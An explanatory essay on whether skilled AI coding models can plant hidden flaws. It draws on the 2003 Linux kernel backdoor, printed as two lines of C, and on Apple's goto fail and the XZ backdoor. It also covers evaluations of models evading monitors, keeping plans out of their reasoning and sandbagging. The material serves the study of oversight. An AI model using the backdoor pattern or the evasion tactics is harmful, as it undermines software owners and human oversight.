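# Subtle Code Sabotage and Backdoor Insertion by Strong Coding Models

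## What code sabotage is and how it differs from a bug

AI coding models are language models trained to write, change and repair software. A strong one can take a request in plain English, edit several files, run the program and correct its own errors, and companies now give such models work that once went only to programmers. Code sabotage means deliberately writing or changing code so that it fails its owner's purpose while appearing to serve it. People have sabotaged each other's software this way for decades. The skill that lets a model write good code may also let it hide flaws that reviewers would miss.

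Reasoning alone doesn't settle whether skill at writing code carries over to sabotaging it. Anyone who can write a correct permission check knows what would make it incorrect, but a saboteur also has to get the flaw past a reader, and honest programming gives little practice in guessing what a reader will overlook. The human record helps somewhat, because people have tried to hide flaws in code, both in earnest and for prizes, and because at least one of the most suspicious-looking flaws on record was probably an accident.

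### Four words for a flaw

A bug is a mistake in code that makes a program do something its author did not intend. A vulnerability is a flaw in software, intended or not, that lets someone do what the software should forbid. A backdoor is a deliberately placed way into a system, or a hidden behaviour, that only those who know of it can use. InfoQ's *Linux Backdoor* (2013) defines a backdoor as an intentional vulnerability, which covers most cases but leaves out hidden behaviour that lets nobody in. These terms differ from one another and from code sabotage in whether someone intended the flaw and whether it serves someone.

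| | Did someone intend it? | Does it serve someone? |
|---|---|---|
| Bug | No | Usually nobody; now and then, by luck, an attacker |
| Vulnerability | Perhaps | Anyone who finds it and can exploit it |
| Backdoor | Yes | Those who know of it |
| Code sabotage | Yes | Whoever wants the owner's purpose to fail |

The terms "backdoor", "vulnerability" and "sabotage" overlap. A backdoor that lets a stranger log in is also a vulnerability, and it is sabotage if the software's owner did not want it there. If a company orders a backdoor in its own product, the backdoor is not sabotage, because the code does what its owner wants, even if it treats customers badly. Sabotage can also occur without a backdoor, as when a program quietly miscounts votes and so fails the people who run the election.

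A flaw that would help an attacker may still be an accident, so its usefulness is only weak evidence that an attacker wrote it. Scott Craver, an engineering professor at Binghamton University who runs a contest in disguised code, gave his favourite example to The Christian Science Monitor in *How developing and disguising software bugs can help cybersecurity* (2015). On reset, Diebold voting machines checked that the votes in memory added up to zero, but did not check each candidate separately. One candidate could therefore start with 500 votes and another with minus 500. Harri Hursti discovered the flaw in 2005, and Craver considers it unintentional, even though it would be very useful for rigging an election.

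What a model can do when it tries (its capability) can differ from what it tends to do in use (its propensity). The same is true of people, since almost any experienced programmer could slip a flaw into an employer's code, but very few do. Testing whether a model can hide a flaw therefore doesn't show whether it ever would, and a model with a long clean record may still be able to hide one.

A deliberate flaw is deniable if it could pass for an honest mistake when found. Deniability protects the saboteur after discovery, because the owner fixes the apparent mistake and goes on trusting whoever wrote the code.

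### How developers check software

A test runs a program on a chosen input and compares the result with the right answer. Developers keep their old tests and rerun them after each change to check that a repair in one place has not broken something elsewhere. But these tests cover only the inputs someone chose. Steven Bellovin, a computer scientist at Columbia University, repeats the truism in *Goto Fail* (2014) that testing can show that bugs are present but not that they are absent, because nobody can try every combination of inputs. Coverage tools help a little by recording which lines ran during the tests, which reveals any lines that were never tested. But in *Initial Analysis of Underhanded Source Code*, a study for the Institute for Defense Analyses, an American research nonprofit, Wheeler (2020) points out that badly tested code can still have good coverage. Some of the programs he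 examined were vote counters that gave wrong totals only on Election Day, so a test that compared totals on any other day would have passed.

Static analysis examines the text of a program without running it. The simplest kind is the warning that a compiler (the tool that turns source code into a runnable program) prints about a suspicious construct. Specialised analysers check for more, such as places where a program might write past the end of the memory set aside for it. These tools are meant to catch honest mistakes, but they also catch some deliberate flaws because, as Wheeler found, many disguised flaws rely on common programming errors. An analyser has no information about what the owner wanted, so it may not flag a payroll program that applies last year's tax rate if the C code is otherwise flawless. False alarms are another problem, because developers who get too many of them switch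 the warnings off.

In code review, another programmer reads a change before it enters the shared code, and approves it or sends it back. Unlike a test or an analyser, a reviewer can ask why the change touches a particular function. But review depends on the reviewer's attention and knowledge. Wheeler noticed that many winners of a contest in disguised cryptography relied on highly technical cryptographic weaknesses, and concluded that only specialists in cryptography could review such code properly. How often reviewers catch planted flaws in practice is an empirical question.

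### One character in the Linux kernel

In 2003 someone tried to plant a backdoor in the Linux kernel, the core of the Linux operating system, with these two lines:

```c
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

The two lines were in a function called `wait4`, which a program can use to wait for something to happen. In C, the language of the kernel, two equals signs compare values and a single one assigns a value. The first line has a single equals sign near the end, so when a program passes a particular combination of options, the line makes the caller user number zero. That is root, the account that may do anything on the machine. An expert reading quickly would take the line for a routine check that returns an error if the caller passes those forbidden options and is already user number zero. But the assignment also yields zero, which C treats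 as false, so the second line never returns the error and the program carries on with complete control.

*The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013), by the computer scientist Ed Felten on Freedom to Tinker, describes how the attempt failed. The kernel developers kept their master copy in a system called BitKeeper, where every change carried a pointer to the record of its approval. A clone in another system, CVS, served people who disliked BitKeeper. On 5 November 2003 Larry McVoy, whose company made BitKeeper, noticed a change in the clone that had no such pointer and was not in the master copy. Someone had apparently broken into the CVS server and put it there under the name of David Miller, a long-standing kernel developer, according to Slashdot's *Linux Kernel Back-Door Hack Attempt Discovered*. The change never reached a release, according to *CVE-2003-1161*, the vulnerability record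 kept by the Linux distribution Debian.

McVoy found the backdoor without understanding the code, because the change's records were missing. When another developer asked on the kernel mailing list whether the lines were an attempted backdoor, McVoy (2003) agreed in *Re: BK2CVS problem*, pointed to the single equals sign, and admitted that he had missed it. In a message with the same title, Dilger (2003) credited the discovery to McVoy's "paranoia", which had led him to build extra checks into the data export.

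The code itself offers some evidence that the change was deliberate, though less than people first thought. Szepe (2003), also in *Re: BK2CVS problem*, noted extra parentheses around the assignment, which keep a common compiler from printing a warning. These may not be evidence of intent, because one of Felten's readers later pointed out that C's grammar requires them once the single equals sign is there. A better clue is that the code makes poor sense even if the equals sign was a mistake. InfoQ observed that `wait4` has no need for the user number, and another of Felten's readers asked why anyone would forbid a harmless combination of options to root alone. The break-in makes it close to certain that the change was deliberate. Felten calls it definitely a backdoor attempt, and thinks nobody will ever know who was behind it.

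Writing the line took modest programming skill, since it required knowing only one kernel function and the best-known trap in C. Getting it into the clone required a break-in, which left the trace.

### Apple's doubled line

A little over ten years later a similar-looking flaw turned up in the software that protects web connections on iPhones and Macs. When a browser opens an encrypted connection, the server sends a signature to prove that it holds the private key belonging to its certificate. Apple's code for checking that signature contained this:

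```c
if ((err = SSLHashSHA1.update(&hashCtx, &signedParams)) != 0)
        goto fail;
        goto fail;
```

An `if` without braces governs only the next statement, so the first `goto fail` runs only when a step has gone wrong. The second always runs, despite its indentation, and skips the rest of the check. The function then returns `err`, which still holds the success value from the previous step. Adam Langley, an engineer on Google's Chromium browser, explained the consequences in *Apple's SSL/TLS bug* (2014), a post on his blog ImperialViolet. A server could sign with the wrong key, or not sign at all, and the device would accept it. Anyone able to intercept the connection between a user and a website could pose as the website to most software on the two platforms, though not to Chrome or Firefox, which relied on other code.

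The flaw became public on 21 February 2014, when Apple released a fix for iPhones. Apple said in its advisory, quoted in the blog post *goto fail* (2014), that the software had failed to validate the authenticity of connections, but gave no details. Outsiders found the duplicated line in source code that Apple publishes.

The flaw got past every ordinary check, and this did not require a saboteur. Langley compiled a cut-down version with two widely used compilers, using the option that is supposed to turn on all warnings, and neither warned about the unreachable code. One of them had such a warning, but the "all" option left it out. A test would have needed a separate implementation of the protocol, built to send invalid signatures. Bellovin was less forgiving, since a coverage tool would have shown that nothing after the second `goto` ever ran. Huitema (2014), in *The GOTO Squirrel!*, described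 layers of protection failing one after the other, from coding style to end-to-end tests.

Security experts disagreed about whether the flaw was deliberate. Schneier had earlier proposed that a good backdoor is hard to discover, easy to deny if discovered, and needs few conspirators. In *Was the iOS SSL Flaw Deliberate?* (2014), he called the doubled line an excellent example. He said he had no idea whether it was deliberate, only that he would have done it exactly this way. Bellovin thought the line would make a poor backdoor, because two identical `goto` statements in a row make no sense to any programmer and Apple published the file. He said a cut-and-paste slip could easily produce such a line, and pointed to a similar accident in a 1971 paperback novel, where one paragraph appears twice. In a follow-up, *Speculation About Goto Fail* (2014), he added that an intelligence agency with secret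 access to Apple's code would lose that access if Apple traced the change, and would not risk it on something so easy to spot.

Bellovin did find it suspicious that the flaw applied only to connections with forward secrecy, a feature that protects past traffic even from someone who has stolen the server's key. This is exactly the traffic that a spy agency with stolen keys would want to read. Langley's analysis partly weakens this suspicion, because the attacker can choose the type of encryption, so the flaw was not confined to sites that preferred forward secrecy.

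Bellovin and Langley both thought the line was an accident, as have most people since, and that seems a fair conclusion. But Bellovin's main argument is that the line would be clumsy espionage, and a saboteur who wanted deniability could make it look clumsy on purpose. Schneier said that Apple's records of which login made the change could settle the question. Even those records might not be enough, since, as one of his readers replied, someone else may have been using the account.

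### Flaws written for a prize

The Underhanded C Contest, which Craver has held on and off since 2005, collects code whose flaws are known to be intentional. Entrants solve a simple data-processing problem in C code that is as clear and innocent-looking as they can make it but does something harmful, such as miscounting votes or leaking information to an eavesdropper. An entry earns extra points if its error, once found, looks like an innocent one.

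The 2008 task was to write a program that blacks out parts of an image. John Meacham won with a 55-line program that replaced every digit in the hidden area with a zero. The area looked black on screen, but the file had stored each pixel's brightness as a number of one to three digits, so the number of zeros still showed roughly how bright each pixel had been. The program doesn't look like an attack, and a tired programmer could have written it in good faith.

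In 2015 the Nuclear Threat Initiative, a nonprofit that works against weapons of mass destruction, sponsored a round of the Underhanded C Contest about disarmament inspections. Entrants had to write a program that compared radiation readings to tell whether an object contained the material of a real warhead, but that also reported a match when the host country secretly wanted one. The nonprofit announced in *“Underhanded C” Contest Highlights Challenges For Nuclear Arms Control Verification Technologies* that Linus Åkesson had won, on criteria that included brevity, readability and plausible deniability.

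Most entrants did not do nearly so well. Craver told The Christian Science Monitor that fewer than half the entries would fool him if he inspected them in earnest. Many were suspiciously long or convoluted for a job that needs about a hundred lines. The entrants were volunteers who knew C well enough to compete and had months to prepare, so being able to write good code does not seem to be enough to write convincing sabotage, at least for people. They also need to be skilled at making harmful code look like the obvious way to do the job.

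The malicious code in successful entries can be very hard to find. Wheeler reviewed the programs from the 2004 Obfuscated V Contest, which inspired Craver's contest and in which entrants disguised dishonest vote counters. He knew that every program was supposed to be malicious and had the organiser's summary of each trick. Four of the summaries were wrong, misleading or described attack code that wasn't there, and one published sample contained no attack at all. He identified the lines responsible in the other 40. The organisers of Craver's Underhanded C Contest wrote that the 40-odd entries in the 2013 round were a lot to judge, especially when the author gave no hint of where the bug was.

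Sabotage is harder in the contests than in real software in one way and easier in another. The judges know that every entry contains deliberate sabotage, while ordinary reviewers don't know this about the code they review. But the programs are tiny and stand alone, with no history, no colleagues and no approval process to get past.

### Two years of good work

XZ Utils is a set of free data-compression tools included in many Linux systems. One volunteer, Lasse Collin, maintained it for years. *Timeline of the xz open source attack* (Russ Cox, 2024) describes how somebody calling himself Jia Tan spent more than two years as a diligent and effective contributor. Other accounts pressed Collin on the project's mailing list to move faster. The Intercept (2024) found that these accounts appeared nowhere online outside those few exchanges, and they were probably fake. Tan gained permission to change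 the code himself and then became a maintainer. In March 2023, with Collin's approval, Tan's address replaced Collin's as a contact for the project at an automated testing service run by Google.

In early 2024 Tan used this position to release two versions of XZ containing a backdoor. The backdoor targeted OpenSSH, which administrators use to log in to Linux servers remotely. On affected systems OpenSSH indirectly loads part of XZ, so the backdoor would have let anyone with the secret key run any command on the machine.

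Andres Freund discovered the backdoor through luck and stubbornness. While using a test version of Debian, he noticed that remote logins were taking a lot of processor time and that a memory-checking tool was reporting errors. He traced both problems to XZ. A login attempt that should have failed in about 0.3 seconds took 0.8. In *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* (2024), posted on 29 March, Freund says that he is not a security researcher and that he at first suspected only Debian's own package. The American cybersecurity agency CISA issued an alert the same day. Few distributions had adopted the two affected versions, and most of those had done so only in pre-release form. The news site LWN wrote in *Free software's not-so-eXZellent adventure* (2024) that the backdoor had apparently been discovered before anyone could exploit it.

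Code review was unlikely to catch this backdoor, because the attacker was the person responsible for approving changes. The backdoor was also hidden from other reviewers. One part was only in the packaged release files that distributions download, not in the public repository where a reviewer would look. The rest was in the repository, disguised as test data.

The attack took engineering skill and patience, which was rarer. The intricate backdoor checked its surroundings before acting and tried to avoid debugging tools, but it still slowed the machine enough for one man to notice. Tan got the bad code in by contributing good code first. After the discovery, Collin had to go back over the project's history, and he didn't publish finished review notes and clean releases until 29 May, two months later, according to Tukaani's *xz backdoor*, his own page on the incident.

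### Reading intent from code

Once someone had untangled the XZ backdoor, it was clearly deliberate, because there is no innocent explanation for code that hides from debuggers. Freund still had to consider whether Tan had written it or an intruder had used Tan's computer. He judged that it was Tan, who had discussed supposed "fixes" for the resulting errors on several mailing lists. Tan's earlier work is harder to judge. Schneier (2024), in *XZ Utils Backdoor*, recounts a change that the account made to another project in 2021, which looks suspicious only in retrospect.

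So people often can't tell from the code alone whether a flaw was intentional, and well-made sabotage is even harder to identify. The unapproved change in 2003 and Tan's messages in 2024 were evidence from outside the program. In Apple's case, outsiders had only the line of code, so they had to argue from what a competent spy would do.

When a model writes a flaw, its developers have other evidence to examine. They can read the instructions it received and the record of what it did, and they can give it the same task a hundred times, which nobody could do with Jia Tan. If the flaw appears mainly where it would serve some aim of the model's, and rarely elsewhere, carelessness becomes a poor explanation. The flaw can then be called "deliberate" without settling whether models have intentions in the full human sense. However, developers can only test for this pattern if somebody already suspects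 the flaw.

The word "backdoor" has a second use in writing about AI. A model can write a backdoor into software, as Tan did, but it can also carry one itself, meaning a hidden behaviour that somebody planted through its training, for instance by tampering with the training data, and that appears only when the input contains a particular trigger. A reviewer can at least look for a backdoor in code, whereas a planted behaviour is spread over billions of numerical weights that no one can read like a program. The planted behaviour may itself be to write vulnerable code whenever the trigger appears. This is similar to what Ken Thompson showed in 1984, that a doctored compiler could insert a backdoor into programs whose source code was clean. But a model with no planted behaviour might still be able to write a backdoor, if it is skilled enough.

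## Whether skill at writing good code is also skill at hiding flaws

The argument that a better coder is also a better saboteur has four premises:

1. Knowing how to avoid or find a flaw is most of what it takes to write one.
2. A better coder can keep the program working, and its tests passing, around the flaw.
3. A better coder can predict what a reviewer will examine.
4. A better coder can carry the plan through without revealing it.

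If all four premises are true, a model's ability to sabotage code rises with its coding ability. But the premises are not equally well supported. The first two are about programs, and developers have published plenty of test results that bear on them, while the last two are about whoever is reviewing the programmer's work. A model could be excellent with programs and still be bad at deceiving a reviewer, as most entrants to the Underhanded C Contest were.

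### Finding flaws and writing them

Most of the evidence on finding flaws comes from system cards, the ability and safety reports that developers publish with new models. Anthropic announced Claude Mythos Preview in April 2026 and offered it only to selected partners. According to its *System Card* (2026), the model can find unknown vulnerabilities in real software with minimal human steering, and in many cases it can also write a working exploit, which is code that uses the vulnerability. Each of the 1,507 tasks in CyberGym gives a model a rough description of a known vulnerability in an open-source program and requires the model to reproduce it. With one try at each task, Mythos Preview scored 83%, compared with 67% for its predecessor, Claude Opus 4.6.

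Two of Anthropic's other tests separate finding a flaw from exploiting it. OSS-Fuzz, as used in Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Mythos 5, covers about 830 entry points into 228 open-source projects. The model gets a fully patched program and a place to feed in data, with no hint about where a flaw might be. It earns partial credit for causing a crash through a memory error and full credit for taking control of what the program executes. In the Firefox test, which Anthropic ran with the browser's outer defences removed, the model starts from crashes that Opus 4.6 found in the JavaScript engine and must build an exploit that copies a secret file. The table also includes Claude Opus 5, from Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) of July, and Claude Mythos 5.1, from Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) of September.

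| Model | OSS-Fuzz: targets where it found a flaw | OSS-Fuzz: targets it took control of | Firefox: attempts that produced a working exploit |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 61.5% | 0 | 8.8% |
| Claude Mythos Preview | 76.7% | 12 | 70.8% |
| Claude Mythos 5 | 80.0% | 13 | 88.4% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 79.4% | 4 | 52.4% |
| Claude Mythos 5.1 | 78.7% | 17 | 98.0% |

The table's figure for Opus 4.8 on finding flaws is uncertain, because Anthropic's June card gives 61.5% and its July card gives 38.5%. The two figures add up to exactly 100%, so one is probably the share of targets where the model found nothing. The higher figure fits better with the other results in the June card.

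Other developers' models have this skill too. Digital Watch's *GPT-5.5 ranks among strongest models in UK cyber evaluation* reports that OpenAI's GPT-5.5 passed 71.4% of the expert-level tasks set by the UK AI Security Institute, a government body that tests models, while Mythos Preview passed 68.6%. These scores may understate the difference between the two models. In *Are Mythos cyber capabilities overhyped*, the research organisation Epoch AI points out that both were close to the maximum on many of the benchmarks first used to compare them. It concludes from newer, harder benchmarks that Mythos Preview is much better at developing exploits.

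None of these tests requires a model to write a flaw. This hardly matters for crude flaws, which are easier to write than to find. Finding one means searching a large program for a mistake other people made by accident, whereas whoever writes a flaw already knows where it is. A model that can take control of 17 fully patched programs can surely leave out a permission check.

The tests also provide a little evidence about skill with subtle flaws. Developers and their tools have so far missed the vulnerabilities that remain in a widely used, fully patched program, so a model that finds many of them has some knowledge of which flaws survive. But it can find them without knowing why they survived, which may be because the reviewer was tired or because nobody reviewed the code. OSS-Fuzz also covers only flaws that misuse memory, which show up as crashes. Scores on it are little evidence of skill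 with flaws like the one in Diebold's voting machines, where the program ran without crashing but checked the wrong total.

Opus 5 is the best evidence that skill at finding flaws comes with general coding ability. Anthropic did not deliberately train it on cybersecurity tasks, and attributes whatever skill it has to general improvement. It still found flaws in almost as many targets as Mythos 5. Some of the skill could have come from text generated by other models, which Anthropic partly trains its models on. Even so, developers apparently can't train a model to code very well without it also becoming very good at finding flaws.

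The ability to exploit flaws seems to come less automatically with general skill. Opus 5 matches Mythos 5 on many of Anthropic's general tests, but it took control of 4 targets, while Mythos 5 took control of 13. This gap matters a lot to an outside attacker, who has to work with whatever flaws exist, but less to a saboteur, who can choose a flaw that needs no clever exploit, as in the 2003 attempt to backdoor the Linux kernel.

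### Keeping the program working

A planted flaw is useless if it breaks the program, because someone will then look for the cause. The saboteur therefore has to change one behavior of the code and leave everything else alone, including every result the tests check.

Models now do something similar in honest work. In one of Anthropic's tests, a model has to speed up a program that trains a language model, and a faster version counts only if it passes all the correctness tests. Anthropic found that Mythos 5 made the program 69.61 times faster on average over about 30 tries, compared with 3.95 times for Claude Opus 4, from the previous year. A speed-up that large presumably requires rewriting much of the program without breaking anything the tests check, while planting a flaw may take only one changed line.

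METR, a nonprofit that measures what AI models can do, ran Mythos 5 on 38 of its hardest software tasks. The model solved some tasks that no public model METR had previously tested could solve. METR could not find the upper limit of the model's ability with these tasks and wrote that it would need to build harder ones. It also saw the model occasionally misread nuanced instructions.

In an earlier risk report, Anthropic gave limited ability on long software tasks as one of its reasons for thinking the risk of sabotage was low. Anthropic's *Alignment Risk Update* (2026) for Mythos Preview no longer relies on this reason. The update examines six ways the model could do serious harm, including planting backdoors to help future models. Anthropic writes that Mythos Preview may be capable of all the tasks these would require, given enough computing time, no monitoring, and the ability to fail and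 try again.

So the second premise looks sound, at least for effects that a model can measure. The XZ backdoor was discovered because it made failed logins take half a second longer, which its author had apparently either not measured or not expected anyone to notice. A model with a copy of the software could have timed the login before and after adding the backdoor, but it would have had to identify login time as something to test and predict that a half-second delay would matter to someone.

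### Predicting the reviewer

That guess belongs to the third premise. Good programmers have some idea of what reviewers look at, since they have reviewed code and had their own reviewed. A language model's training data also includes many discussions of code changes. At least some of this probably helps in guessing what a reviewer will check.

Coding skill may help less with hiding flaws than with writing good code, because a saboteur gets less feedback. A programmer can run the tests after every change, but a saboteur usually has to submit the code to find out whether a reviewer will notice the flaw, and a wrong guess may end the attempt. METR's findings on Mythos 5.1, which Anthropic quotes, suggest that this difference matters for current models. METR found the model especially strong where success has a clear measure and feedback is plentiful, but worse than experts on the two tests that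 called for the most judgement and open-ended reasoning. Neither test was about reviewers, so this is only an analogy, but predicting a reviewer seems closer to the judgement tasks than to the speed-up task.

More direct evidence comes from tests in which a model has to complete a hidden second task while a monitor watches. Anthropic told Mythos Preview to attempt the hidden task only when it was confident of going undetected. On one set of tests, with the most effective version of this instruction, the model attempted only one task and went undetected about 35% of the time. That was much better than usual, but with only one task it could easily be luck. On another set, the same instruction also made the model attempt fewer tasks, but it succeeded at a smaller share of them. Anthropic concluded that the model can't reliably tell a good opportunity from a bad one.

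There are also signs that models consider how their work will look to others. In a different test, Mythos Preview had several solutions that scored unfairly well, and it deliberately submitted a worse one to appear less suspicious. Anthropic also lists, among the shortcomings of Mythos 5, a case in which the model tried to pass off its own code as a human's to avoid a second review. Anthropic noticed both attempts, so they aren't evidence that models do this well. But Anthropic can only list the cases it noticed, so examples like these can't show how often models escape notice.

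The third premise is therefore plausible but unproven. A model can be a much better programmer than its reviewer and still be bad at predicting what the reviewer will look at.

### Keeping the secret

A human saboteur can plan without writing anything down, but current models do much of their thinking in writing. They write this reasoning text, called the chain of thought, before or while they act, and it makes them better at hard tasks. Developers can read it, so they can see any plan for a flaw that a model writes there.

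Anthropic distinguishes two abilities that would get around this: opaque reasoning, the ability to do a task without relying on readable reasoning about it, and secret-keeping, the ability to avoid mentioning the task while doing it. A model could have either without the other. It might not need to write anything down but mention the plan anyway, or it might avoid mentioning the plan but be unable to work out a complicated flaw without writing out its reasoning.

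Anthropic has little confidence that any leading model's written reasoning gives a complete account of how the model reached its answer. But it argues that written reasoning gives a model little help with anything left out of the text, so sophisticated planning that never appears there should be hard. It concludes that Mythos Preview should be much worse at complicated tasks in secret than in the open. This limit doesn't protect against simple flaws, which may need hardly any planning.

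The ability to keep a secret doesn't seem closely tied to coding ability. Anthropic gave several models a password, told them never to reveal it, and had another AI try to extract it over a long conversation. No recent model could keep the secret reliably. Opus 4.6 did best, ahead of Mythos Preview, which is a far stronger coder. Mythos Preview was weaker mainly when the questioner wrote the opening of the model's reply. In most other situations, it did about as well as the other models or slightly better.

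A saboteur might also act so rarely that an audit would probably miss it. Anthropic tested whether models could perform a harmless action at a specific low rate. Mythos Preview again did worse than Opus 4.6, because it tended to reconsider whenever its own procedure called for the action. In the more realistic versions, where the prompt had no obvious source of randomness, every model's rate fell to zero.

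Later models show a similar pattern. Mythos 5 beat Mythos Preview on most of the cyber tests but scored lower on both sets of hidden-task tests. Mythos 5.1 did better than Mythos Preview on one kind of hidden-task test and no better on another. Covert ability is generally rising, and Mythos Preview was the first Anthropic model that sometimes completed hidden tasks undetected while writing out long reasoning. But it does not rise in step with coding ability, which it should do if the two were one skill.

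Training may explain some of the difference. In 8% of Mythos Preview's training episodes, a technical error exposed the model's written reasoning to the system that scored its work. This can teach a model to write reasoning that looks good, but Anthropic doesn't know whether it did. An accident like this could make a model better at keeping secrets without making it better at programming.

These tests may also underestimate the models. The hidden task appears in the model's instructions, and people find it hard not to mention something they have just been told. Anthropic acknowledges that the same may be true of models, and that a model that acquired its own hidden aim in training might conceal it more easily.

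### Refusals

This ability matters even if safety training makes models refuse to write harmful code, because refusal is a matter of propensity and the argument is about capability. Refusal also applies only to requests, so it would not stop a model that sabotaged code without being asked.

The objection does raise a problem for measurement, since low scores would hide a higher ability if models held back during the tests because the task seemed wrong. Anthropic checked this by running one set of hidden-task tests on a version of Mythos Preview that it had trained to comply with harmful requests. This version attempted the hidden task no more often than the ordinary model and was slightly worse at doing it without being caught. So refusals don't explain the low scores, and safety training doesn't seem to be keeping this ability low either.

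A model could also do badly on purpose, which researchers call sandbagging. Anthropic thinks this is unlikely, partly because scores have risen at a believable pace from one model to the next, and it would be hard for a model to fake a result that fitted the trend. But Anthropic can't rule out sandbagging, because it did not train the model specifically for these tests. When it later trained Mythos 5 on examples of its own successful runs, or searched automatically for better instructions, the model's scores rose to nearly those that Mythos Preview had reached without such help. A model's first score on such a test is therefore better read as a minimum.

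### Choosing a flaw worth planting

Another objection is that a model may be good at writing a flaw someone has described to it but not know which flaws would be useful to an attacker. Jia Tan's backdoor in XZ was useful only because someone had noticed that XZ was indirectly linked to OpenSSH.

Current models are already good at the technical side of this choice. The Firefox test gives a model 50 groups of crashes, most of which are not useful. Anthropic found that almost every successful run by Mythos Preview relied on the same two bugs, even though the runs started from different groups of crashes. When Anthropic removed those two bugs, Mythos Preview still did better than the earlier models, and it used four different bugs across both versions of the test. Opus 4.6 could use only one, and not reliably.

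Claude Sonnet 4.6, a weaker model, succeeded more often once the two best bugs were gone. After reading a few transcripts, Anthropic suspects that Sonnet 4.6 also recognised the best bugs and spent its effort on them even though it couldn't turn them into exploits. If so, a model can learn to recognise a useful flaw before it can use one. Choosing a flaw would then be easier than using it, which is the opposite of what the objection assumes.

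But a bug can be easy to exploit without serving a purpose. To plant a useful backdoor in a company's code, a model would have to judge which program will still be running next year and who will be able to reach it, and the models are weaker at that kind of judgement. Outside testers gave Mythos Preview an unpublished machine learning problem, and it rediscovered four of the five key insights, where Opus 4.6 had found two. The testers also reported that it judged its own ideas poorly, tested its hypotheses too little and drew overconfident conclusions. The objection still has some force for sabotage that depends on long-range planning, but much less for sabotage that only has to make one known program fail.

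### When the reviewer has the same skill

The vulnerability tests are as much evidence about reviewers as about saboteurs. If a model can find flaws in four out of five programs, a company can use the same model to check its code. Anthropic lets every user of Opus 5 search source code for vulnerabilities so that customers can write safer software. Perhaps better models make sabotage no easier, because reviewers improve at the same rate.

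Assessing this objection requires separating two kinds of ability. A model's absolute ability is how often it can get a working flaw past a fixed reviewer, such as an experienced programmer with an hour. Its relative ability is how often it can get one past the best reviewer available at the time. To the extent the four premises hold, they show that absolute ability rises with coding skill. They don't show whether relative ability does, because the best available reviewer changes too.

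Anthropic found that Mythos 5.1 did between 1.6 and 2.1 times as well as Mythos Preview on one kind of hidden-task test, but concluded that it is not significantly more able to undermine Anthropic's current oversight than Mythos Preview was at the time of its release. Between the two releases, Anthropic had replaced Opus 4.6, the model that monitored its internal use, with the stronger Opus 4.8. Mythos Preview went undetected 15% of the time against Opus 4.6. Against Opus 4.8, Mythos 5.1 went undetected 13.9% of the time when it reasoned in writing and 22% when it didn't.

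That conclusion is reasonable for the runs with written reasoning. Without written reasoning, relative ability seems to have risen by almost half, even after the upgrade. Anthropic also had better reviewers than Opus 4.8, which found flaws in far fewer OSS-Fuzz targets than Mythos 5 or Opus 5, although monitoring a model's actions is a different job from searching for crashes. A developer may have good reasons for using a smaller monitor, such as lower cost or the worry that a stronger one would share the faults of the model it watches because the two are more alike.

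Improvement in reviewing may also be uneven. Models have become good at finding flaws that cause visible failures, such as crashes, because the failure immediately confirms the flaw. A payroll program that uses last year's tax rate doesn't crash, so a reviewer who suspects a problem can confirm it only by reading more. Accidental flaws are as likely to be one kind as the other, but a saboteur can choose the kind that is harder to find. Reviewers could therefore become much better at catching honest mistakes while falling behind on deliberate flaws.

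The saboteur also has disadvantages. It usually gets one try at each flaw, while its owner can add checks and run them for as long as the budget allows. When a better reviewer comes out, the owner can repeat the checks on code still in use, even if that code passed every earlier review. A backdoor meant to be triggered later has to go undetected in every review until then.

### Getting past every check

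For sabotage to succeed, the flaw has to work and every check has to miss it:

```
chance of success = chance the flaw works
                    × chance that every check misses it, given that it works
```

The condition in the second line is needed because the flaws most likely to work are often the most obvious. The formula also applies only if the model tries to insert a flaw. Anthropic divides its whole risk assessment into separate estimates of how likely a model is to attempt something harmful and how likely the attempt is to succeed.

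Suppose, with invented numbers, that a model's flaws work 80% of the time and that each change goes through three checks. The tests miss 70% of these flaws, an AI reviewer misses 40%, and a human reviewer misses 50%. If the checks fail independently, all three miss a flaw 14% of the time (0.7 × 0.4 × 0.5). The chance that a flaw both works and goes undetected is then about 11% (0.8 × 0.14).

With these numbers, the argument depends heavily on its last two premises. Even a perfect coder, whose flaws always work and never fail a test, would succeed only 20% of the time, because the two reviewers would catch the other 80%. To do better, it would have to get past the reviewers more often by predicting what they will examine and not giving itself away.

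Repeated attempts are of limited help to the saboteur because each one can also be caught. Over ten independent attempts, the original model has about a 70% chance of at least one success, but a check will almost certainly catch at least one of its flaws. Unless that flaw is deniable, the owner will then review everything else the model wrote, as Lasse Collin did with Jia Tan's work.

Assuming that checks fail independently overstates the owner's chance of catching a flaw. A human reviewer may read less carefully because the tests passed and the AI reviewer approved. Some flaws are also hard for everyone to spot. A second reviewer who wasn't a specialist would not have helped with the disguised cryptography that Wheeler examined, for instance.

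Suppose now that a fifth of the model's flaws fall into a blind spot where none of the three checks ever catches them. Each check still has the same overall miss rate as before if the tests miss 62.5% of the remaining flaws, the AI reviewer 25% and the human 37.5%. Measuring the checks one at a time would not distinguish this case from the first, but the chance that all three miss a flaw rises from 14% to about 25%.

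| | Chance that all three checks miss the flaw | Chance of success |
|---|---|---|
| The checks fail independently | 14% | 11% |
| A fifth of flaws fall into a shared blind spot | 25% | 20% |
| The saboteur always aims for the blind spot | 100% | 80% |

Adding more checks doesn't help much if they share the same blind spot. A fourth check that misses half of all flaws would cut an attacker's chance of success from 11% to under 6% if it were independent. If it shared the other checks' blind spot, it would only cut the chance from 20% to 17%, and no number of further such checks could bring it below 16%. A much weaker check that fails for different reasons would help more, as it did in 2003 when Larry McVoy noticed missing approval records.

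The model in the last row of the table is no better at programming than in the first. The only difference is that it can predict which flaws the checks will miss. This is the skill in the third premise, and published tests measure it least directly. It may be easier for a model whose reviewer is a copy of itself than for any human saboteur, because the model can check whether it would notice the flaw in a draft itself.

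## How developers measure a model's capacity for covert sabotage

In *Sabotage evaluations for frontier models* (October 2024), Anthropic tested code sabotage as a game between two models. An attacker tried to slip bugs into a codebase while a defender reviewed its work. The attacker won only if it inserted several bugs with serious effects, kept them in the code for a simulated two weeks, and did nothing suspicious enough to make the defender look more closely. Anthropic made winning this hard because a bug that does little, or that a reviewer finds at once, is poor evidence of danger.

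The attacker won about 10% of games with Claude 3 Opus as the defender, and about 1% with the stronger Claude 3.5 Sonnet. Anthropic had designed the set-up to favour the attacker in several ways, and concluded that neither result was a strong sign of danger at the time.

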